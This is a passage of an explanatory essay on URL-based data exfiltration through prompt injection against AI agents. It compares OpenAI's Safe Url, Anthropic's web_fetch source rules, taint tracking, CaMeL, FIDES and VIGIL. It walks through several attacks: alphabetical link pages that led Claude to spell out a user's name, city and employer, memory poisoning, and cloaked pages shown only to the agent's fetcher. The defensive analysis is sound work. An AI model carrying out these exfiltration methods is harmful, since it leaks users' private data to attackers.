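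The index rule also wouldn't work for notify_url. The operations team's webhook is a private address, so a crawler shouldn't have recorded it, and the software would flag the legitimate notice. The attacker could make confirm.example.net/receipt a public page and get it indexed. The software would then accept the address and send the attacker the customer reference in the message field. OpenAI designed the rule for fetching pages and images, where the address is the main way data can leak. A tool with a message field needs a rule about who supplied the destination or what the message contains.

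OpenAI says the safeguard doesn't make a page's content trustworthy or prevent a site from deceiving its visitors. A reset link on reset.example.net could be in the public index and still lead to a fake login page.

The check must also run everywhere an agent can send a request. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* says the system, called Safe Url, covers page visits in its Atlas browser and both searches and page visits in Deep Research. Embrace The Red found that OpenAI had left earlier protections out of its macOS and iOS apps. A developer who adds a new outbound tool can easily repeat this mistake.

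### The exception in web_fetch

Anthropic's rule for web_fetch allowed Claude to fetch a URL only if it had already appeared in certain parts of the conversation. *Web fetch tool*, Anthropic's documentation as of June 2026, lists these as user messages, results from tools that the developer runs, and results from earlier searches or fetches. Claude could not fetch an address it had made up. A planted instruction to attach the customer reference to an address therefore failed, because the finished address had not appeared in any of those places.

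When Anthropic released the tool in September 2025, Willison praised the ban on invented addresses but noticed a problem with the first source. Many applications paste emails or documents into the "user message" they send to the model. The software then treats an attacker's address in that text as the user's, much as OpenClaw treated messages from anyone in a group chat as its owner's.

Ayush Paul exploited a different source, the links inside pages that Claude had already fetched. Willison (2026) explains in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that Paul built a site where he claimed to need an AI assistant to identify its user. Since the assistant couldn't type into a form, it was told to find the user's profile by following alphabetical links, with each page offering links for the next letter. Claude spelled out the user's name this way, and also revealed the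 user's home city and employer, which it knew from its memory of past conversations.

This is ZombieAgent's method, except that each page supplies the next set of links. The attacker therefore doesn't need to prepare a separate address for every position or put them all in one message. The links never repeat, so a ban on repeat visits wouldn't help. Paul's server showed the false login page only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude's fetching tool, so a suspicious user who opened the site would have seen nothing odd. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* notes that asking Claude to summarise such a site could start the attack, and that websites use details like a home town in security questions.

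Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and paid no bounty. It then stopped web_fetch from following links in pages the tool had fetched. Anthropic had documented the exception since the tool's release, so the software had worked as designed. The designers presumably wanted to let an agent follow a link from a supplier's status page to the full incident report. After the fix, the agent can open that report only if the user supplies its address or a search returns it.

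The fix does not extend to the default settings for developers who use web_fetch in their own applications. Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, a newer Chinese edition of the documentation, still lists links from fetched pages as permitted by default. It says developers can use the `url_sources` setting to switch off each source or restrict it to particular tools. A developer can reproduce the fix by accepting URLs from search results and refusing those from fetched pages.

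The same documentation describes a way for a model to get its own address accepted. If the agent also has a tool that runs code, the model can write a short program that prints an address containing the customer reference. The address then appears in the tool's result, so web_fetch accepts it by default, even though the model wrote it. An error message that quotes the model's input has the same effect. Developers can exclude such tools by name, but any tool they add later is accepted unless they also exclude it. If they list the accepted tools instead, a new tool stays excluded until somebody adds it to the list.

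Web_fetch also rejects URLs that seem to contain a password or API key, unless that credential appears in the user's text or the developer's standing instructions. This check might catch a whole key, but it wouldn't catch a customer reference or a key split across several URLs.

The Claude app still permits URLs from search results, and attackers can get their own pages into those results, as the two campaigns that Zscaler found had already done. An attacker with enough indexed pages might instruct Claude to search for certain words and open particular results. This is harder than Paul's attack because the attacker has to control what the search returns.

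### Taint tracking

Checking whether an address appeared earlier is a simple form of taint tracking, a much older technique for ordinary programs. The software labels data from untrusted sources, copies the label to anything computed from that data, and checks for it before a sensitive operation. A web application might label a visitor's input and keep it out of database commands until another function has made it safe.

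For `notify_url`, the software would label the status page "untrusted" when the agent fetches it. The attacker's address would keep this label when it became the `url` argument, so the software would refuse the call or ask the user. The outage summary comes from the same page, so it would also have the label, but a policy could allow untrusted text in the `message` argument when the destination is trusted. A separate "private" label on the customer reference would stop it from being sent to anyone outside the company.

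Software can track a value through each operation of an ordinary program but not through a language model, an obstacle that automated code analysis also meets. If the system treats all output as untrusted once the agent has read one untrusted page, the agent can't send the outage notice after reading the status page. If the system marks only output that repeats untrusted text word for word, it misses paraphrases, encodings and a choice among prepared links.

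A workable compromise for destinations is to accept a `url` argument only if it exactly matches an address in the developer's settings. An attacker can then influence which trusted address the model picks, as with the forty customers' webhooks, but can't add a new one. If there is only one trusted address, the attacker can only cause or prevent a notice and affect its text.

A label also has to match whoever wrote the text. The fetch tool receives the supplier's incident report and the planted comment as one page from status.supplier.example. If the operator has marked that site as trusted, the comment gets the supplier's label. To separate the two, the software would have to parse the page's layout and identify which parts outsiders can write. Labeling each site is easy, but the label can be badly misleading on a site that accepts comments.

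An agent's long-term memory makes it harder to judge a URL by its source. According to Radware, OpenAI had barred ChatGPT from opening an attacker's URL stored in its memory, and from using memory in a chat after using connected services such as Gmail. Babo reversed the order, so that ChatGPT used memory first and then Gmail. A shared file planted an instruction in memory to read a certain email whenever the user sent a message, and the email supplied the links. ChatGPT was allowed to use that source at the time, but the instruction to read the email came from the attacker's file. To catch this, the software would have to store the file's label with the memory and apply it to whatever the memory led the agent to do.

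Even so, labels are useful against credential-reset phishing. The software could detect that the link to reset.example.net in the outage notice came from a web page and not from the company's settings, and remove it or show its source next to it. The engineer would then know that the agent hadn't verified the link. The false claim about expired passwords would still reach the engineer, because the software can match a link to its source much more reliably than it can match a paraphrased sentence.

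### CaMeL and FIDES

Two research systems from 2025 keep untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions, so they don't have to track how a label passes through a model.

Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at Google, Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich described CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). One model sees the user's request and writes a program for the whole task before the agent reads anything from outside. A separate model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted text and returns values. For the supplier example, the program would look roughly like this:

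```
page = fetch("https://status.supplier.example")
report = read_without_tools(page, "Is anything down? Summarise.")
if report.down:
    notify_url(url="https://hooks.example.com/ops",
               message=report.summary)
```

The planted comment can't add a call to confirm.example.net, because the planning model never receives the comment and the program contains only one notification. An interpreter runs the program and labels each value with its source and permitted recipients. Before each tool call, it checks these labels against the operator's policies. Software can track the labels exactly here because they pass through ordinary program steps. Everything the reading model returns keeps the label of the text it read.

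On AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, travel and banking tasks for agents, CaMeL completed 77% of tasks with its security guarantee, compared with 84% for an undefended system. Those figures come from the revised paper; the first version reported 67% for CaMeL. A loss of seven percentage points is moderate, but benchmark tasks may be easier to plan in advance than a company's own tasks. The guarantee also depends on the quality of the security policies, which someone has to write.

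CaMeL's guarantee covers what the agent does, so a false statement in a summary can still get through. The reading model could write in its summary that customer passwords have expired and include the reset link, and the program would send that summary to the team's channel as planned. CaMeL would need an additional policy on links to stop the phishing notice.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft, 2025) describes FIDES, which keeps the usual loop in which the model chooses one step at a time. FIDES labels data by how trustworthy it is and by who may see it. It can store an untrusted page in a variable and show the planning model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to a tool, or have a separate model without tools answer a narrow question about the page. If the planning model reads the page itself, its context becomes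 untrusted, and the policy can then forbid sensitive calls for the rest of the task.

If the question is whether anything is down, and the answer can only be "yes" or "no", the attacker can influence one bit. An operator could reasonably accept that much influence over a notice with fixed wording. A free-text summary doesn't limit the attacker's influence to one bit.

Costa and colleagues report that FIDES can complete a broad range of AgentDojo tasks with its guarantees in place. How much these guarantees limit the agent depends mostly on the kind of task. The planning model doesn't need to see the untrusted text when the user's request already determines the steps. But if the text has to determine the next step, either the agent gives up the protection or the software refuses the action.

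Lin, Zhou and colleagues (2026) criticise fixed plans for this reason. In *VIGIL*, they tested defences on 959 attacks in which a hostile provider controls a tool's description, results or error messages. A false error might tell the agent to use a "backup" tool. They report that rigid defences typically completed fewer than 12% of tasks under attack, because a plan written in advance leaves the agent no way to recover when a tool fails. They cite work by Debenedetti and colleagues as an example of the approach, but the 12% figure covers rigid defences in general, not CaMeL specifically.

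In VIGIL, the agent explores several courses of action, and a language model checks each against limits derived from the user's request before anything runs. This more than doubled the share of completed tasks from 12%, but most may still have gone unfinished, and about 8% to 12% of the tool-based attacks succeeded. Lin and colleagues also tested VIGIL on a benchmark they built themselves. Attackers who control a tool have more power than someone commenting on a status page, so the results probably overstate the drawbacks for the supplier example.

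### "Register at the address in this document"

Suppose a user uploads an invitation to a trade workshop and asks the agent to register at the address in the document. The organiser wrote the address, and the user may never have looked at it. A strict provenance rule would block the address because it came from retrieved content, even though the user asked the agent to use it.

CaMeL's planning model could write a correct program for this: read the document, extract the URL, open it and submit the form. But the URL would be labeled untrusted when it reached the tool, so a policy that blocks confirm.example.net would also block the workshop URL. The two cases differ only in what the user meant. The user pointed to the document as the source of the workshop URL, whereas a stranger added confirm.example.net when the user had asked for a status report.

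The other rules wouldn't handle the case any better. OpenAI's index would accept a public registration page but flag a personal invitation link, which is unique to its recipient and so looks like an address containing private data. Under Anthropic's rule, the result could depend on whether the application pasted the document's text into the user message. If it did, web_fetch would accept the organiser's address and any address an attacker had hidden in the same document.

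A more precise rule would let the user's request authorise one source for one purpose. The planning model would record that the destination must come from this invitation, and the software would allow a single registration there with only the user's name and email address. It would still reject URLs from other pages. This limits what an attacker can gain, but if the invitation is fake, the user has authorised the attacker's URL.

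So the software should ask the user before submitting the form. It can show the full address, identify the invitation as its source, and list the details it will send. Only the user can confirm that they know the organiser, and one question per registration is a tolerable interruption.
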